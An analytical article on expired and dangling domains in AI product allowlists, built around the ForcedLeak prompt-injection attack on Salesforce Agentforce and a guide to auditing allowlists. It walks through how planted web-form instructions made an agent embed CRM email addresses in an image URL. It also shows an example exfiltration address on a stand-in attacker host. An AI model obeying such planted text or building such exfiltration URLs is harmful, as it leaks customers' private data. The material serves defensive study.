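# Expired and Dangling Domains in AI Product Allowlists

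## What a domain allowlist does and how a trusted name changes hands

A domain allowlist names the only domains that software may contact or load content from. Makers of AI assistants and agents use these lists to keep private data inside the product. Suppose a vendor lists example.com, stops paying for the registration a few years later and forgets to remove the domain from the list. A stranger then registers it for a few dollars, and the assistant's requests to example.com still go through because the domain is still on the list.

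The stranger has acquired residual trust, which is the trust that systems still place in a domain name after it has changed hands. Ordinary websites have the same problem. In an AI product, an outsider may also be able to combine indirect prompt injection with a specially built web address to make the product send private data to the trusted name.

### How data leaves through a web address

A language model receives its instructions and the material it works on as one stream of text, and it does not reliably distinguish them. In indirect prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by planting instructions in data that an AI system later reads and follows. *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* (Martin, 2025) describes a typical route. An attacker types instructions into a public web form, and the company's database stores them with the rest of the entry. When an employee later asks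 the AI about that entry, the model reads the planted text and acts on it as if the employee had written it. The attacker needs no account and no contact with the employee.

Web pages can carry planted instructions too. According to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*, Google repeatedly scanned an archive of the public web and saw malicious cases rise by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. That figure is relative and doesn't measure how common the attacks are. Neither Google nor the security company Forcepoint found sophisticated, coordinated campaigns.

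An attacker can use planted instructions to make a model look something up, but the attacker still has to receive the answer. Sending data to a party who should not have it is called exfiltration, and requesting a web address is enough to do it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that whoever runs a website receives the full address of every request, and that websites commonly log those addresses. A request for `https://attacker.example/collect?data=...` therefore delivers whatever follows the equals sign, even if the server sends nothing back.

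Images make this work without a click:

1. The planted text tells the assistant to look up, say, a customer's email address.
2. It also tells the assistant to end its answer with an image whose web address contains what it found.
3. The user's browser requests the image in order to display the answer.
4. The attacker reads the email address in the server's log.

The image does not have to exist, because the request itself sends the data. The user may see nothing odd except a broken image.

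Willison's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* (2023) describes how a prompt injection could make ChatGPT encode private data and put it in the URL of an image hosted on any site. The security blog Embrace The Red had reported the flaw to OpenAI and Microsoft early that year. Microsoft fixed it in Bing Chat in May 2023 with a Content Security Policy that generally kept the chat page from loading images (Embrace The Red, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*).

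### Lists that the browser enforces

A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a header, a line of text that a website sends to the browser with a page, listing the sources the page may load from. It was originally meant to limit attacks that inject scripts into web pages. The current text of the standard, *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), is a working draft from W3C, the body that standardizes web technology. It recommends CSP as a second layer of defense rather than the first.

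A policy consists of directives, one for each type of content, and each directive has its own allowlist. The directive for images is `img-src`. If a policy has no `img-src`, the browser uses the general directive, `default-src`. If that is missing too, the policy does not restrict images. An allowlist entry can be an exact host name or a wildcard such as `*.example.com`.

The matching rule for host names is short. For an exact entry, the browser checks that the requested host is the same string, ignoring upper and lower case. For a wildcard entry, it removes the asterisk, which leaves `.example.com` with the dot in front, and checks whether the requested host ends with that string. A page with the policy `img-src *.example.com` therefore behaves like this:

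| Host in the image's address | Ends with `.example.com`? | Result |
|---|---|---|
| cdn.example.com | Yes | Image loads |
| img.eu.example.com | Yes | Image loads |
| example.com | No, the leading dot is missing | Browser blocks it |
| notexample.com | No, the leading dot is missing | Browser blocks it |
| example.com.attacker.net | No | Browser blocks it |

The third row surprises people because a wildcard covers every subdomain at any depth but not the bare domain, so allowing both requires two entries.

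The browser also compares the scheme (`https` or `http`), the port and, if the entry includes one, the path. CentralCSP, a reference site on the header, notes that the browser does not compare the query string, the part of an address after the question mark. A policy that allows `https://cdn.example.com/c.png` also allows the same address with a customer's email address in the query string. CSP therefore does not limit the data a page can send to an allowed host through the query string.

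In a short advisory section of the draft, W3C says that CSP can reduce exfiltration if a site uses the policy to list the servers a page may communicate with. A policy without `default-src` cannot provide this protection, because some kinds of request, such as prefetching (loading a page before the user asks for it), have no more specific directive. The protection is also only as good as the most permissive list in the policy. W3C's example, `default-src 'none'; img-src *`, looks strict but lets images carry data to any server.

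The second warning applies to old entries. A policy may have a strict `default-src` and dozens of sound entries, but a single `img-src` entry whose domain now belongs to someone else still gives the new owner a way to get data out. Only that owner can use the hole, so it is far narrower than `img-src *`, but it works just as well for them.

### Lists that a proxy enforces

CSP restricts what a browser loads for a page. It has no effect on code that an agent runs on a remote machine, where there may be no browser. The usual control there is an egress allowlist, which limits outbound network traffic from the agent's sandbox (the isolated environment where its code runs). The operator routes that traffic through a proxy, a program that checks the host name in each request and either forwards or drops the request. The list then applies to everything the agent runs, including package installers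 and download tools.

Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, lets users limit its internet access with such a list. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, setup scripts for a cloud task run with full internet access, but the agent that takes over afterwards has none by default. A user who turns access on can start from an empty list, allow every domain, or use a preset of about 70 domains commonly needed to download software, such as alpinelinux.org and yarnpkg.com. The user can add domains to the empty list or the preset.

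OpenAI illustrates the danger with an example in which Codex is asked to fix a bug. The bug report contains a command, presented as a way to reproduce the bug, that sends the latest commit from the user's code repository to an outside server at httpbin.org. The preset list would block the command because httpbin.org is not on it. OpenAI also lets users block all requests except GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, which are meant for retrieving information. That would block the command too, since it uses POST, which is meant for submitting data. However, a GET request can still leak data in the query string of its address. If a listed domain changed hands, its new holder could collect data this way even with both restrictions on.

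The two kinds of list may be converging. Chrome is testing a header called Connection-Allowlist, which blocks redirects by default. CentralCSP describes it as an addition to CSP rather than a replacement.

### Why neither list notices a new owner

Both controls compare names. The CSP matching procedure uses the requested address, the list, the page's own origin and the number of redirects so far. Neither it nor a proxy that filters by host name uses information about who holds the domain or when it was registered. Once a name matches, the domain name system (DNS), which translates names into network addresses, directs the request to whatever server the current holder has chosen.

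HTTPS encryption does not help when a domain has changed hands. The certificate can show that the server is authorized to act for the domain name, but certificate authorities issue one to anybody who can prove control of the domain at the time, and a new holder can do so without deception.

OpenAI doesn't rely on lists of trusted sites, partly because strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them. Another reason is that many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a check of only the first address can approve a request that ends at an attacker's server. CSP reduces this second problem because the browser checks the new address against the list after each redirect. But that doesn't help when an attacker has taken over a listed domain, because the attacker already controls the first address and doesn't need a redirect.

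A defender needs information from outside the list to notice a new owner. *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* (2025), a paper on websites that load resources from other people's domains, proposes blocking any resource whose domain was registered after a chosen cutoff date. The dates come from WHOIS, the public registration records, or from stored observations of past DNS traffic. The paper applies the same check to domains in CSP allowlists. It also warns that when a domain a site depends on expires, the expiry can go unnoticed for months.

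### How control of a name is lost

An attacker can gain control of an allowlisted domain if its registration lapsed, a subdomain points to a resource its owner gave up, or nobody ever registered the name. These cases are worth distinguishing because they need different checks and fixes.

**The registration lapses.** The registrable domain is the part of a host name that someone registers and renews, such as example.com in cdn.example.com. A lapsed domain is one whose registration has ended and that anyone may now register. The new holder controls the bare name and can create any subdomain under it, so they can set up a server that matches the allowlist entry, whether that entry is an exact host or a wildcard.

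Roth, Barron and colleagues used the Internet Archive's old copies of web pages to trace how 10,000 highly ranked domains had deployed Content Security Policy (CSP), and found allowlists that an attacker could bypass through expired or mistyped domains. domaincontroller's reading notes, *Deployed CSP Analysis*, quote nine cases of a domain expiring after a site had listed it and seven domains that were unregistered while on a list. These counts are minimums because the researchers lacked zone files, the registries' lists of existing domains, for part of the period.

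Search results can also retain trust in expired domains. *Домен умер, но поисковик о нём помнит* (Antipov, 2026) reports on a test in which the company AIR Security tried about 2,000 queries typical of AI assistants and examined some 6,500 sites. It found 36 unregistered domains that still appeared in the search results. One of them, pyquestions.com, came up for a question about a Python error. Anyone who registered such a name could put instructions on the page and wait for an agent to read them. The attacker would use the domain to deliver an injection, rather than to get data out as with an allowlisted domain. AIR Security described a possible attack and gave no evidence of mass compromise.

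**A subdomain's DNS record dangles.** The owner still holds example.com, but one of its subdomains has a dangling DNS record, which points to a resource that the owner has given up and another party may be able to claim, such as a deleted site on a cloud hosting service. An attacker who claims that resource controls what the subdomain serves, which is known as subdomain takeover. The attacker gets only that host, which is enough if the allowlist names it. If the list has a wildcard entry, the attacker can use any vulnerable subdomain, including ones the list's author doesn't know about.

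*Can I Take Your Subdomain?* (2020) looked for this combination on live websites. It classes a policy as exploitable when the policy lists a vulnerable subdomain and taking over that subdomain gives the attacker the abilities the attack requires. For instance, injecting a script requires the ability to place a file on the server, while collecting data from image requests requires the ability to read the addresses of incoming requests.

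**Nobody ever registered the name.** A typing error in an allowlist can produce an entry for a domain that does not exist, which an attacker can then buy. Language models are a newer source of such names. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, gave two models 685,339 prompts about 913 brands and collected 2.1 million distinct addresses. It reports about 250,000 unregistered domains among them, but the safer figure is about 87,630. That is the number of nonexistent addresses with an unregistered root domain in the group's own breakdown, which is hard to reconcile with the larger total. The other nonexistent addresses were invented paths or subdomains on domains that do exist.

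Attackers have started to use such names. Unit 42 found a phishing kit aimed at a domain that it had flagged as a likely invention 23 days earlier. Unit 42 studied links in models' answers, not allowlists, but it warns that developers copy generated addresses into working code. An invented name could enter an allowlist drafted with an assistant's help in the same way.

ForcedLeak, an attack that the security company Noma demonstrated in 2025 on Agentforce, Salesforce's AI agent product, exploited a lapsed domain registration. Martin quotes Noma's explanation that Salesforce's allowlist still contained my-salesforce-cms.com after the registration had expired and anyone could buy the name. Willison likewise writes in *ForcedLeak* that the wildcard entry for the domain was still in Salesforce's CSP header after the expiry, and that the researchers registered the name. SecurityWeek also describes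 an expired domain. Some press accounts call the problem a DNS misconfiguration, which suggests a dangling record instead.

The difference between an expired domain and a dangling record affects how to find and fix the fault. The owner of a dangling record can delete it because they still own the domain around it. Salesforce no longer held my-salesforce-cms.com, so it couldn't fix the problem by correcting a DNS record. It had to recover the name or remove it from the allowlist. A scan for dangling records across the domains Salesforce still owned would have missed the problem.

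## How the ForcedLeak attack on Salesforce Agentforce worked

Salesforce sells customer relationship management (CRM) software, which companies use to keep records of customers and sales prospects. Its Agentforce platform lets those companies build AI agents that read and act on the records. In the ForcedLeak attack of July 2025, Sasi Levi and colleagues at Noma Labs, Noma's research group, used only a public web form and a $5 domain to get an Agentforce agent to send them email addresses from such records.

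Most of the public evidence comes from Noma's post *ForcedLeak* (2025), which RST Forums, a security forum, copied in full. SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* notes that Noma had recently raised $100 million. Noma sells security for AI agents, so it had a commercial reason to make the flaw look serious. But the post includes the planted text and part of Salesforce's allowlist, so readers can check some of Noma's claims against them.

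### Planting the instructions

Noma first asked an Agentforce agent what color you get by mixing red and yellow, and the agent answered "Orange". Noma concluded that the agent would handle requests unrelated to Salesforce data, and that an attacker could exploit this.

The color test is weaker evidence than it looks, because the theft depended on a request for the email addresses of sales leads (potential customers), which is an ordinary request for a CRM agent. An agent that refused every off-topic question might still have fulfilled that request.

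The researchers then needed a way to get text in front of the agent without an account. They chose Web-to-Lead, a Salesforce feature that saves whatever a visitor types into a web form as a new lead in the CRM. Companies use it to collect contacts at conferences and in marketing campaigns. Noma switched the feature on and compared how much text each field of the form accepts:

| Field | Limit in characters |
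|---|---|
| First Name | 40 |
| Last Name | 80 |
| Company | 40 |
| Email | 80 |
| Description | 42,000 |

Noma judged the first four fields too short and the Description field ideal, because it has room for long instructions with many steps. The text Noma eventually planted is only about 400 characters long. That is still too long for the four short fields, which hold 240 characters combined, but it takes up only about 1% of the Description field. It would have fitted even if Salesforce had limited that field to 1,000 characters.

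The planted text consists of four numbered requests, worded as if a lead had sent in some questions:

1. The first asks how many leads the company has.
2. The second repeats the question about red and yellow.
3. The third asks for the leads' email addresses and tells the agent to write any space as %20, the code for a space in a web address.
4. The fourth asks for a "preview image" at the end of the reply and supplies the HTML code for it. The image's address is on cdn.my-salesforce-cms.com, and its query string has a placeholder for the answer to the third request.

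The HTML also labels the image "Customer Logo". Browsers normally show this label when an image fails to load, so an employee would probably have seen those words and perhaps a broken image.

Noma doesn't explain why it included the first two requests, but they may have helped the text pass for a real inquiry. The answer to the color question is also easy to recognize, so the researchers would have known from "orange" in the reply that the agent was working through their list.

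### From the employee's request to Noma's server

The planted text does nothing until an employee asks the agent about that lead. Noma also wrote the employee's request, which was to check the lead named "Alice Bob", respond to the lead's questions, and then draft an email to the lead with the results.

Noma describes this as a standard business request, and a salesperson could plausibly write something like it. But Noma also labels it the "final optimized" prompt, which means the researchers had adjusted the wording until it suited them. Because the agent is asked to answer whatever the lead asked, it is more likely to treat planted questions as part of its job than if the employee had requested a one-line summary of the lead.

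Noma showed that the attack was possible, but doesn't report how often it succeeded when the researchers repeated it. Language models can respond differently to the same text, so the attack may not have worked every time. Noma also doesn't report whether a plainer request would have worked.

After the employee sent the request, the agent looked up the leads' email addresses in the CRM and ended its reply with the image code, which had those addresses in the image URL's query string. The employee's browser then automatically requested the image from Noma's server at cdn.my-salesforce-cms.com, sending the email addresses with the request.

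Noma rented the server from Amazon Lightsail, a service for small websites and applications. The researchers set it up to log every request, pick out the data in the query string and alert them immediately.

The browser sent the data out in the address it requested, so a company looking for traces of such an attack should search its logs of requested addresses rather than look for suspicious image files. Some press accounts are unclear about this. The Hacker News, for instance, describes the data as leaving "in the form of a PNG image".

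A second trace may remain in the CRM, because the planted text stays in the lead's record until somebody deletes it. It can be there for months before an employee asks about that lead. Noma therefore advised Agentforce customers to check their existing leads for submissions with unusual instructions or formatting.

### What the image allowlist permitted

Salesforce's CSP should have stopped the browser from requesting an image from a stranger's server. Noma published the image allowlist from its `img-src` directive. Three of the items are not host names: they cover the page's own origin and images that the page already contains or creates itself. The other 22 are host entries, and they fall under 20 registrable domains. Sorted by name (registration records might show different holders), they look like this:

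| Apparent owner | Registrable domains | Entries |
|---|---|---|
| Slack, which belongs to Salesforce | slack.com, slack-edge.com, slack-edge.mil, slack-edge-gov.com, slack-gov-dev.com, slack-imgs.com, slack-imgs.mil, slack-imgs-gov.com, slack-imgs-gov-dev.com, slack-imgs-mil-dev.com, slack-mil-dev.com | 12 |
| Salesforce | force.com, my-salesforce.com, my-salesforce-cms.com, salesforce.com, salesforce-experience.com, sfdcstatic.com | 7 |
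| Other companies | amazonaws.com, cloudinary.com, twimg.com | 3 |

The entry for the lapsed domain was the wildcard `*.my-salesforce-cms.com`. To match it, Noma created a subdomain that begins with `cdn`, a common label for servers that deliver images.

A person reading the list would have been unlikely to notice the lapsed domain, which anyone could buy. It is one of 17 domains, out of 20, that appear to belong to Salesforce or Slack, and it differs from another entry, `*.my-salesforce.com`, by four characters. The other three are Amazon, Cloudinary and Twitter's image domain, so a reviewer who removed only the names that looked foreign would have removed those three and kept the lapsed domain.

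Other entries also suggest that nobody had pruned the list for some time. The entry `*.vf.force.com` is redundant, because `*.force.com` already covers it. Four of the Slack domains end in "-dev", which suggests they are for development rather than for customers. Every extra domain is another registration that somebody has to keep renewing, though neither of these oddities is a vulnerability in itself. A lapse is less of a risk for the two .mil domains, because only the US military can register .mil names and a stranger couldn't buy them.

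Neither Noma nor Salesforce has explained what my-salesforce-cms.com was for. CMS usually stands for content management system, software for publishing web content, and Salesforce has a product of that kind. A University of Sydney table of Salesforce addresses lists an address under cdn.salesforce-experience.com for that product's public content. We can only guess from the name that the lapsed domain once served the same purpose, or that Salesforce reserved it and never used it.

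### Whether the attack needed the lapsed domain

The header that Noma published gives good reason to doubt that Noma needed the lapsed domain to get the data out. Noma calls the discovery of the domain essential and writes that exfiltration "would have been impossible" without bypassing the CSP, a phrase Martin repeats. Readers could easily take this to mean that the data could not have been exfiltrated without the lapsed domain.

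The same image list contained `*.amazonaws.com` and `*.cloudinary.com`. Amazon Web Services rents storage to the public, and many of its customers' files have addresses under amazonaws.com. For example, image addresses in a Substack newsletter from the security company Zellic include the host substack-post-media.s3.amazonaws.com. An attacker could rent storage there too, and the browser would accept an image address under amazonaws.com just as it accepted Noma's.

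The attacker would also have to see the full addresses of incoming requests, including the query string. Amazon's storage service can give its customers logs with this detail, so the Amazon entry looks usable. It is less clear whether an ordinary account at Cloudinary, which stores and delivers images, would show the same detail.

All of this is an inference from the header. Noma doesn't report trying either entry, and another control in Agentforce might have blocked an attack through them. Still, *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk*, by the security company PromptArmor, advises Salesforce customers to avoid this type of entry, a wildcard that allows any site hosting user-generated or otherwise untrusted content.

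If the inference is right, the $5 domain purchase was convenient but not necessary for getting the data out. Noma's server was already on rented Amazon equipment, and the lapsed domain only gave it a name that the browser would accept. Removing my-salesforce-cms.com from the allowlist would then have closed Noma's route but left a similar one open through Amazon. Checking an allowlist only for lapsed registrations would miss this second route, because Amazon has never lost control of amazonaws.com.

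The lapsed domain looked like Salesforce's own, which was an advantage for an attacker. According to SecurityWeek, using a trusted Salesforce domain gave the attack a significant chance of going undetected. A security analyst who saw requests to cdn.my-salesforce-cms.com from an employee using Salesforce would probably not have been suspicious.

Noma's claim is also too broad if read literally, because an image policy restricts only images and an agent may have other ways to send data out. In April 2026, Capsule Security disclosed another attack on Agentforce, PipeLeak, which also began with instructions in a public lead form. According to Claw Times, the agent retrieved CRM data and emailed it to the attacker, so the attacker needed no allowlisted domain. Capsule found no cap on the amount of data. Salesforce replied that it had fixed the specific scenario and that agents now need human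 confirmation by default before taking email actions.

PipeLeak shows that an agent can leak CRM data even if its image allowlist contains no unsafe domains. But it came nine months after Noma's report, so it doesn't prove that the email route was open in July 2025.

### Disclosure and repair

Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection* gives the following timeline:

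| Date in 2025 | Event |
|---|---|
| July 28 | Noma reports the flaw to Salesforce |
| July 31 | Salesforce acknowledges the report |
| September 8 | Salesforce begins to enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI, its other set of AI features |
| September 25 | Noma publishes the attack |

Salesforce introduced the new control on September 8, six weeks after the report, and Noma waited another 17 days before publishing. The copy of Noma's post on RST Forums lacks the September 8 line, but Martin also gives the date, and TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* quotes it from Salesforce's announcement.

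Trusted URLs is an allowlist of the external addresses an agent may use in its output, and each customer's administrators maintain it. Salesforce presented it as a second line of defense for cases where an agent obeys planted text. In an alert quoted by The Hacker News, the company describes it as protection against data leaving "after a successful prompt injection".

Salesforce also regained control of my-salesforce-cms.com and, according to Willison, audited and corrected the CSP header before introducing Trusted URLs. Noma's post shows only the old header, so it is unclear whether the correction also removed the wildcards for Amazon and Cloudinary.

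Between Noma's report and September 8, Salesforce also restricted what agents could do without permission. Its *Security Advisories* for August 14 and 25 list ten Agentforce actions that now require a person's confirmation, including canceling an order, resetting a password and updating a customer's contact details. Salesforce gave prompt injection as the reason but called the changes proactive and did not mention Noma. The changes would not have stopped ForcedLeak as Noma demonstrated it, because the agent in that attack only looked up data and displayed an image, and none of the ten actions does either.

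The public record doesn't show exactly when the registration of my-salesforce-cms.com lapsed or when Salesforce recovered the domain. SecurityWeek places the recovery after Noma's report, and Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* lists it among the fixes Salesforce had completed by September 8, which leaves a window of six weeks. None of the accounts explains how Salesforce got the domain back, though Noma, which had bought it, presumably gave it up.

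The date of the lapse matters more to customers, because it determines how long a stranger had the chance to buy the domain and receive their data. The published accounts don't establish whether that was a few weeks or several years. The domain was unregistered when Noma bought it, but an earlier buyer could have registered it for a year and let it lapse again.

Customers with old enough logs can partly check this. The employee's browser requested the image, so a company that records its employees' web traffic could search for any address under my-salesforce-cms.com. A match would not prove theft, since the domain may have served ordinary content while Salesforce still held it. Email addresses or other CRM data in the query string would be much stronger evidence.

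### What Salesforce disclosed about abuse

Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* prints Salesforce's full press statement, which Hackread also received. The company acknowledged Noma's report and said it had released patches that stop agents from sending output to untrusted addresses. It said prompt injection remains "a complex and evolving area" and that it would keep investing in security controls.

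In the statement, Salesforce did not say whether anyone other than Noma had used the flaw. It had addressed that question for another component, the Aura Controller, a few months earlier. After media reports about a security issue there in June 2025, Salesforce wrote on its advisories page that it had found no evidence of exploitation. That page, which runs to October 2, 2025, has no entry for ForcedLeak.

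This difference supports only a modest conclusion. Neither Infosecurity Magazine nor Hackread reports asking Salesforce about abuse and getting no answer, and no public account identifies a victim. Salesforce may have had no abuse to report, or it may have lacked the logs to find out, because stolen data would have traveled from a customer's browser to the attacker's server without passing through Salesforce's systems.

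### The severity score

Press reports gave ForcedLeak a severity score of 9.4 out of 10 on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), where scores of 9.0 and above are critical. *Salesforce Agentforce hit by Noma ForcedLeak exploit* (Çelebi, 2025) attributes the score to Noma. Hackread reports that the score was initially 9.1 and later rose to 9.4, but doesn't explain why.

A CVSS score is calculated from ratings of a flaw, including how easily an attacker can reach it, whether a user must act first, and how badly it affects the secrecy, accuracy and availability of data. Noma's post gives the score without these ratings, so outsiders can't check the calculation or see what changed between 9.1 and 9.4.

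Noma scored the flaw 9.4 but didn't specify in its post which version of CVSS it used. Under version 3.1, a flaw that exposes data but doesn't let an attacker change data or disrupt a service can score at most 8.6. If Noma used that version, it must have counted some ability to change data or disrupt the service, and the researchers demonstrated neither. The newer version 4.0 calculates scores differently.

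The number is therefore not a reliable guide to how urgently to treat a similar flaw. It is more useful to know that the attacker needed no account, that an employee had to ask the agent about the lead, and that the exfiltrated data consisted of email addresses.

### What Noma demonstrated and what the publicity added

The demonstration supports the claim that text from a public form made an Agentforce agent look up email addresses and put them into an image URL, and that the browser then sent them to a domain Salesforce no longer controlled but still trusted. Noma's logs are the evidence for the last step. Salesforce confirmed the essentials by acknowledging the report, changing its product and taking the domain back.

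Noma's post also lists sales pipeline data, internal communications and years of customer history as being at risk. This is a reasonable extrapolation, because the same image trick works for any text that the agent can retrieve. A company's potential losses would have depended on what its agent had permission to read. Noma doesn't state how many email addresses it collected or whether a single request could carry a large database.

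Noma also writes that attackers could manipulate CRM records, establish lasting access and move on to connected systems. The image trick alone would not be enough for this. An agent can change a record only if its builder has given it an action for doing so, and the planted text would have to trigger that action. Such an attack is possible in principle, and Salesforce evidently took the possibility seriously when it added confirmation steps in August. But Noma does not describe altering a record or reaching another system in its demonstration.

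Commentators disagree about how new the attack was. Noma calls it "an entirely new attack surface". Willison calls it a classic example of the "lethal trifecta", his term for an AI system that has access to private data, reads untrusted content and can communicate with the outside world. Itay Ravia, the head of Aim Labs, told The Hacker News that it was a variant of EchoLeak, an earlier attack on a Microsoft product in which planted text led to data theft without the user clicking anything. Aim Labs, which belongs to a security vendor, discovered EchoLeak, so Ravia had an interest in stressing the resemblance.

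Willison and Ravia have the stronger argument about the injection and the image, since researchers had shown both in chat assistants by 2023. The lapsed domain is more distinctive, although Roth and colleagues had already found expired domains in the CSP allowlists of ordinary websites. Noma's contribution was to show that an expired domain in an AI product's allowlist could complete a theft of private records.

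Other vendors' publicity made the attack sound more current than it was. Varonis' *ForcedLeak and the Future of AI Agent Security* (2025) was updated on October 30, more than seven weeks after Salesforce began enforcing Trusted URLs, yet it calls the exploit "actively exploitable". The phrase describes what an attacker could do to a vulnerable agent. It is not evidence that anyone did this, though a reader could easily think criminals were using the attack at the time.

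Incident databases can magnify this effect. OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce AI* (2026), an entry in an AI incident monitor, covers PipeLeak and a related flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Studio. The entry's summary, labelled "AI generated", describes vulnerabilities that Capsule Security discovered, but the accompanying assessment classes them as having been "exploited in practice". Anyone using such entries to count real attacks on Agentforce should first check whether the researchers were the only attackers.

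Noma's advice to customers also deserves some caution where it overlaps with the company's products. In its post, Noma recommends central inventories of AI agents, real-time detection of prompt injection and strict controls on the tools an agent may call. It says such runtime controls would have prevented ForcedLeak, but reports no test of them. Salesforce could have blocked the image that Noma used at any time, without buying anything, by deleting `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` from the header.

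## Finding every place an AI product trusts a domain

The lapsed domain in ForcedLeak was in a CSP header, but an AI product may keep allowlists in other places too. A coding agent can have one for its chat page, another for its sandbox and a third written by the customer's staff. A reviewer should therefore start by finding all the lists and recording who maintains each one, who can read it and what it lets through.

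| Place | Who maintains it | Who can read it | What a listed domain gets |
|---|---|---|---|
| CSP header | Vendor | Anyone who can open the page | Browsers load images, scripts or other content from it |
| Link and image filter on the model's output | Vendor or customer | Often only the customer | The product shows links or images that point to it |
| Sandbox egress preset | Vendor | Anyone, if the vendor publishes it | Code that the agent runs can contact it |
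| Connector settings | Whoever adds the connector | Usually only the customer | The connector exchanges data with it |
| Login-redirect list | Developer of the app or connector | Outsiders can see only the address in use | The login service sends sign-in codes to it |
| Browser-extension permissions | Developer of the extension | Anyone who installs the extension | The extension works on its pages or accepts messages from them |
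| Customer's own entries | Customer's administrators or users | Only the customer | The same as any other entry on that list |

### Lists in the browser and on the model's output

CSP headers are the easiest to read. The command `curl -sI https://www.example.com` prints the headers of a public page. A chat page behind a login may have a different policy from the home page, and the reviewer can read it in the browser's developer tools.

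Report URI's *CSP at Dropbox* prints a live header from Dropbox, which sends two policies with the same page. A reviewer needs to read both. One contains the keyword `'strict-dynamic'`, which makes modern browsers ignore the host names listed for scripts and rely on a one-time code from the server instead. A lapsed domain in that script list would therefore do little harm in a modern browser, but the keyword has no effect on the image list.

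Some sites put the policy in the page's HTML rather than in a header, so a reviewer who checks only headers will miss it. Roth, Barron and colleagues crawled 10,000 popular sites in June 2019 for *Complex Security Policy* and found that 78 of the 1,206 sites with a policy had it only in the HTML.

Filters on the model's output are harder to find because vendors build them in different ways. Salesforce's Trusted URLs is one example, and GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs AI agents as automated jobs on code repositories, is another. According to GitHub's *Network Permissions*, one setting controls which domains the agent can contact and which links can appear in its output. The product replaces links to unlisted domains with "(redacted)". One bad entry therefore lets the agent both contact the domain and output links to it, and the link filter still uses the list if somebody turns the firewall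 off.

A Chrome extension lists the domains it trusts in its `manifest.json` file. The `host_permissions` field lists the sites whose pages the extension may work on, and `externally_connectable` lists the websites that may send it messages. If a domain in `externally_connectable` lapses, whoever registers it next could send messages to the extension, and the damage would depend on which messages the extension accepts.

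### Connectors and logins

Connectors link an agent to outside services, often through a common standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). They are easy to overlook because their traffic may bypass the sandbox's allowlist. In Claude Code's cloud sessions, this traffic travels through Anthropic's servers, so users don't have to list a connector's host (Anthropic's *Cloud environments*). GitHub warns that the firewall for its Copilot cloud agent doesn't cover MCP servers or the setup steps that a customer configures. The inventory therefore needs a separate line for every connector's address.

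Claude Code also has a list of trusted hosts outside the environment's allowlist. Users can store an API key as a "network secret" and name the hosts that should receive it. Anthropic's proxy adds the key to requests for those hosts, and sessions can generally reach them even if the allowlist omits them. If one of those domains lapsed and someone else registered it, the new holder would get the key along with the data in any request they received.

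When someone connects an account through OAuth, the usual standard for this, the login service redirects the browser to an address that the app's developer registered in advance. The redirect includes a short-lived code, which the app exchanges for access to the account. Outsiders normally can't read the full list of registered addresses, but they can see the one in use in the sign-in page's URL, after `redirect_uri=`.

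### Entries that customers add

Customers can extend most of these products' lists, and a vendor's documentation won't show what they added. Finding the entries may take some work:

- **Copilot:** Organization owners and, by default, repository administrators can both add entries, and GitHub combines the two sets.
- **Claude Code:** Each environment has its own list, and administrators can't push one list to everybody's environments. A company's entries may be scattered across its employees' personal settings, although it can also offer a shared environment.
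- **Claude Science:** Members of an organization manage the list for this research tool on their own computers by default. Anthropic also lets the organization take over the list, which sets aside whatever members had added.
- **Codex:** For cloud tasks the list is in each environment's settings, and for local use it is in a file called `managed_config.toml` (PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist*).

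Old settings can also survive an upgrade. GitHub keeps firewall rules that customers saved in an earlier format. Docker's sandboxes also have a preset allowlist, and Docker reuses a preset from an earlier installation without prompting the user.

Allowlist entries also come from other companies' instructions. CodeRabbit, which sells automated code review, tells Claude Code users in its *Network requirements* to keep Anthropic's default domains and add CodeRabbit's. If CodeRabbit ever gave up one of its listed domains, it could correct its instructions, but it couldn't delete the entry from its customers' allowlists.

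Corporate firewalls belong in the inventory too. GitHub's *Copilot-Zulassungslistenreferenz*, the German edition of its allowlist reference, lists addresses for companies to allow through their firewalls. One is `usagereports*.blob.core.windows.net`, for downloading usage reports from Microsoft's cloud storage. The asterisk covers any storage account whose name begins with "usagereports". Microsoft's customers choose their account names, so a stranger could presumably create one that matches.

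A reviewer should copy entries exactly as written, because the same text can cover different hosts in different products:

| List | What `example.com` covers | How to include subdomains |
|---|---|---|
| CSP | That host only | Add `*.example.com` |
| Claude Code, custom entries | That host only | Add `*.example.com` |
| Kiro, custom entries | That host only | Write `.example.com`, which also covers the bare name |
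| Copilot, custom entries | The host and all its subdomains | Already included |
| GitHub Agentic Workflows | The host and all its subdomains | Already included |

A company that moved its custom entries from Claude Code to Copilot without changing them would therefore allow many more hosts than before.

### Five published presets compared

OpenAI, GitHub, Anthropic and Amazon all publish the domains that their agents' sandboxes can reach, so outsiders can check the lists without an account. The figures for Claude Code come from Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments* and those for Claude Science from Anthropic's *Network requirements*, both as of July 2026. Amazon last updated its page for Kiro, its coding agent, on October 2, 2026.

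| Product | Entries | How the vendor writes them | Wildcards | Stated promise of upkeep |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI Codex | 71 | Mostly whole domains | 0 | Yes |
| GitHub Copilot cloud agent | 216 | Mostly exact hosts; 6 entries include a path and 2 are IP addresses | 6 | None |
| Claude Code cloud sessions | 202 | Whole domains and exact hosts | 14 | None |
| Claude Science | 72 | Mostly exact hosts | 17 | None |
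| Kiro | 73 | Mostly whole domains | 0 | None |

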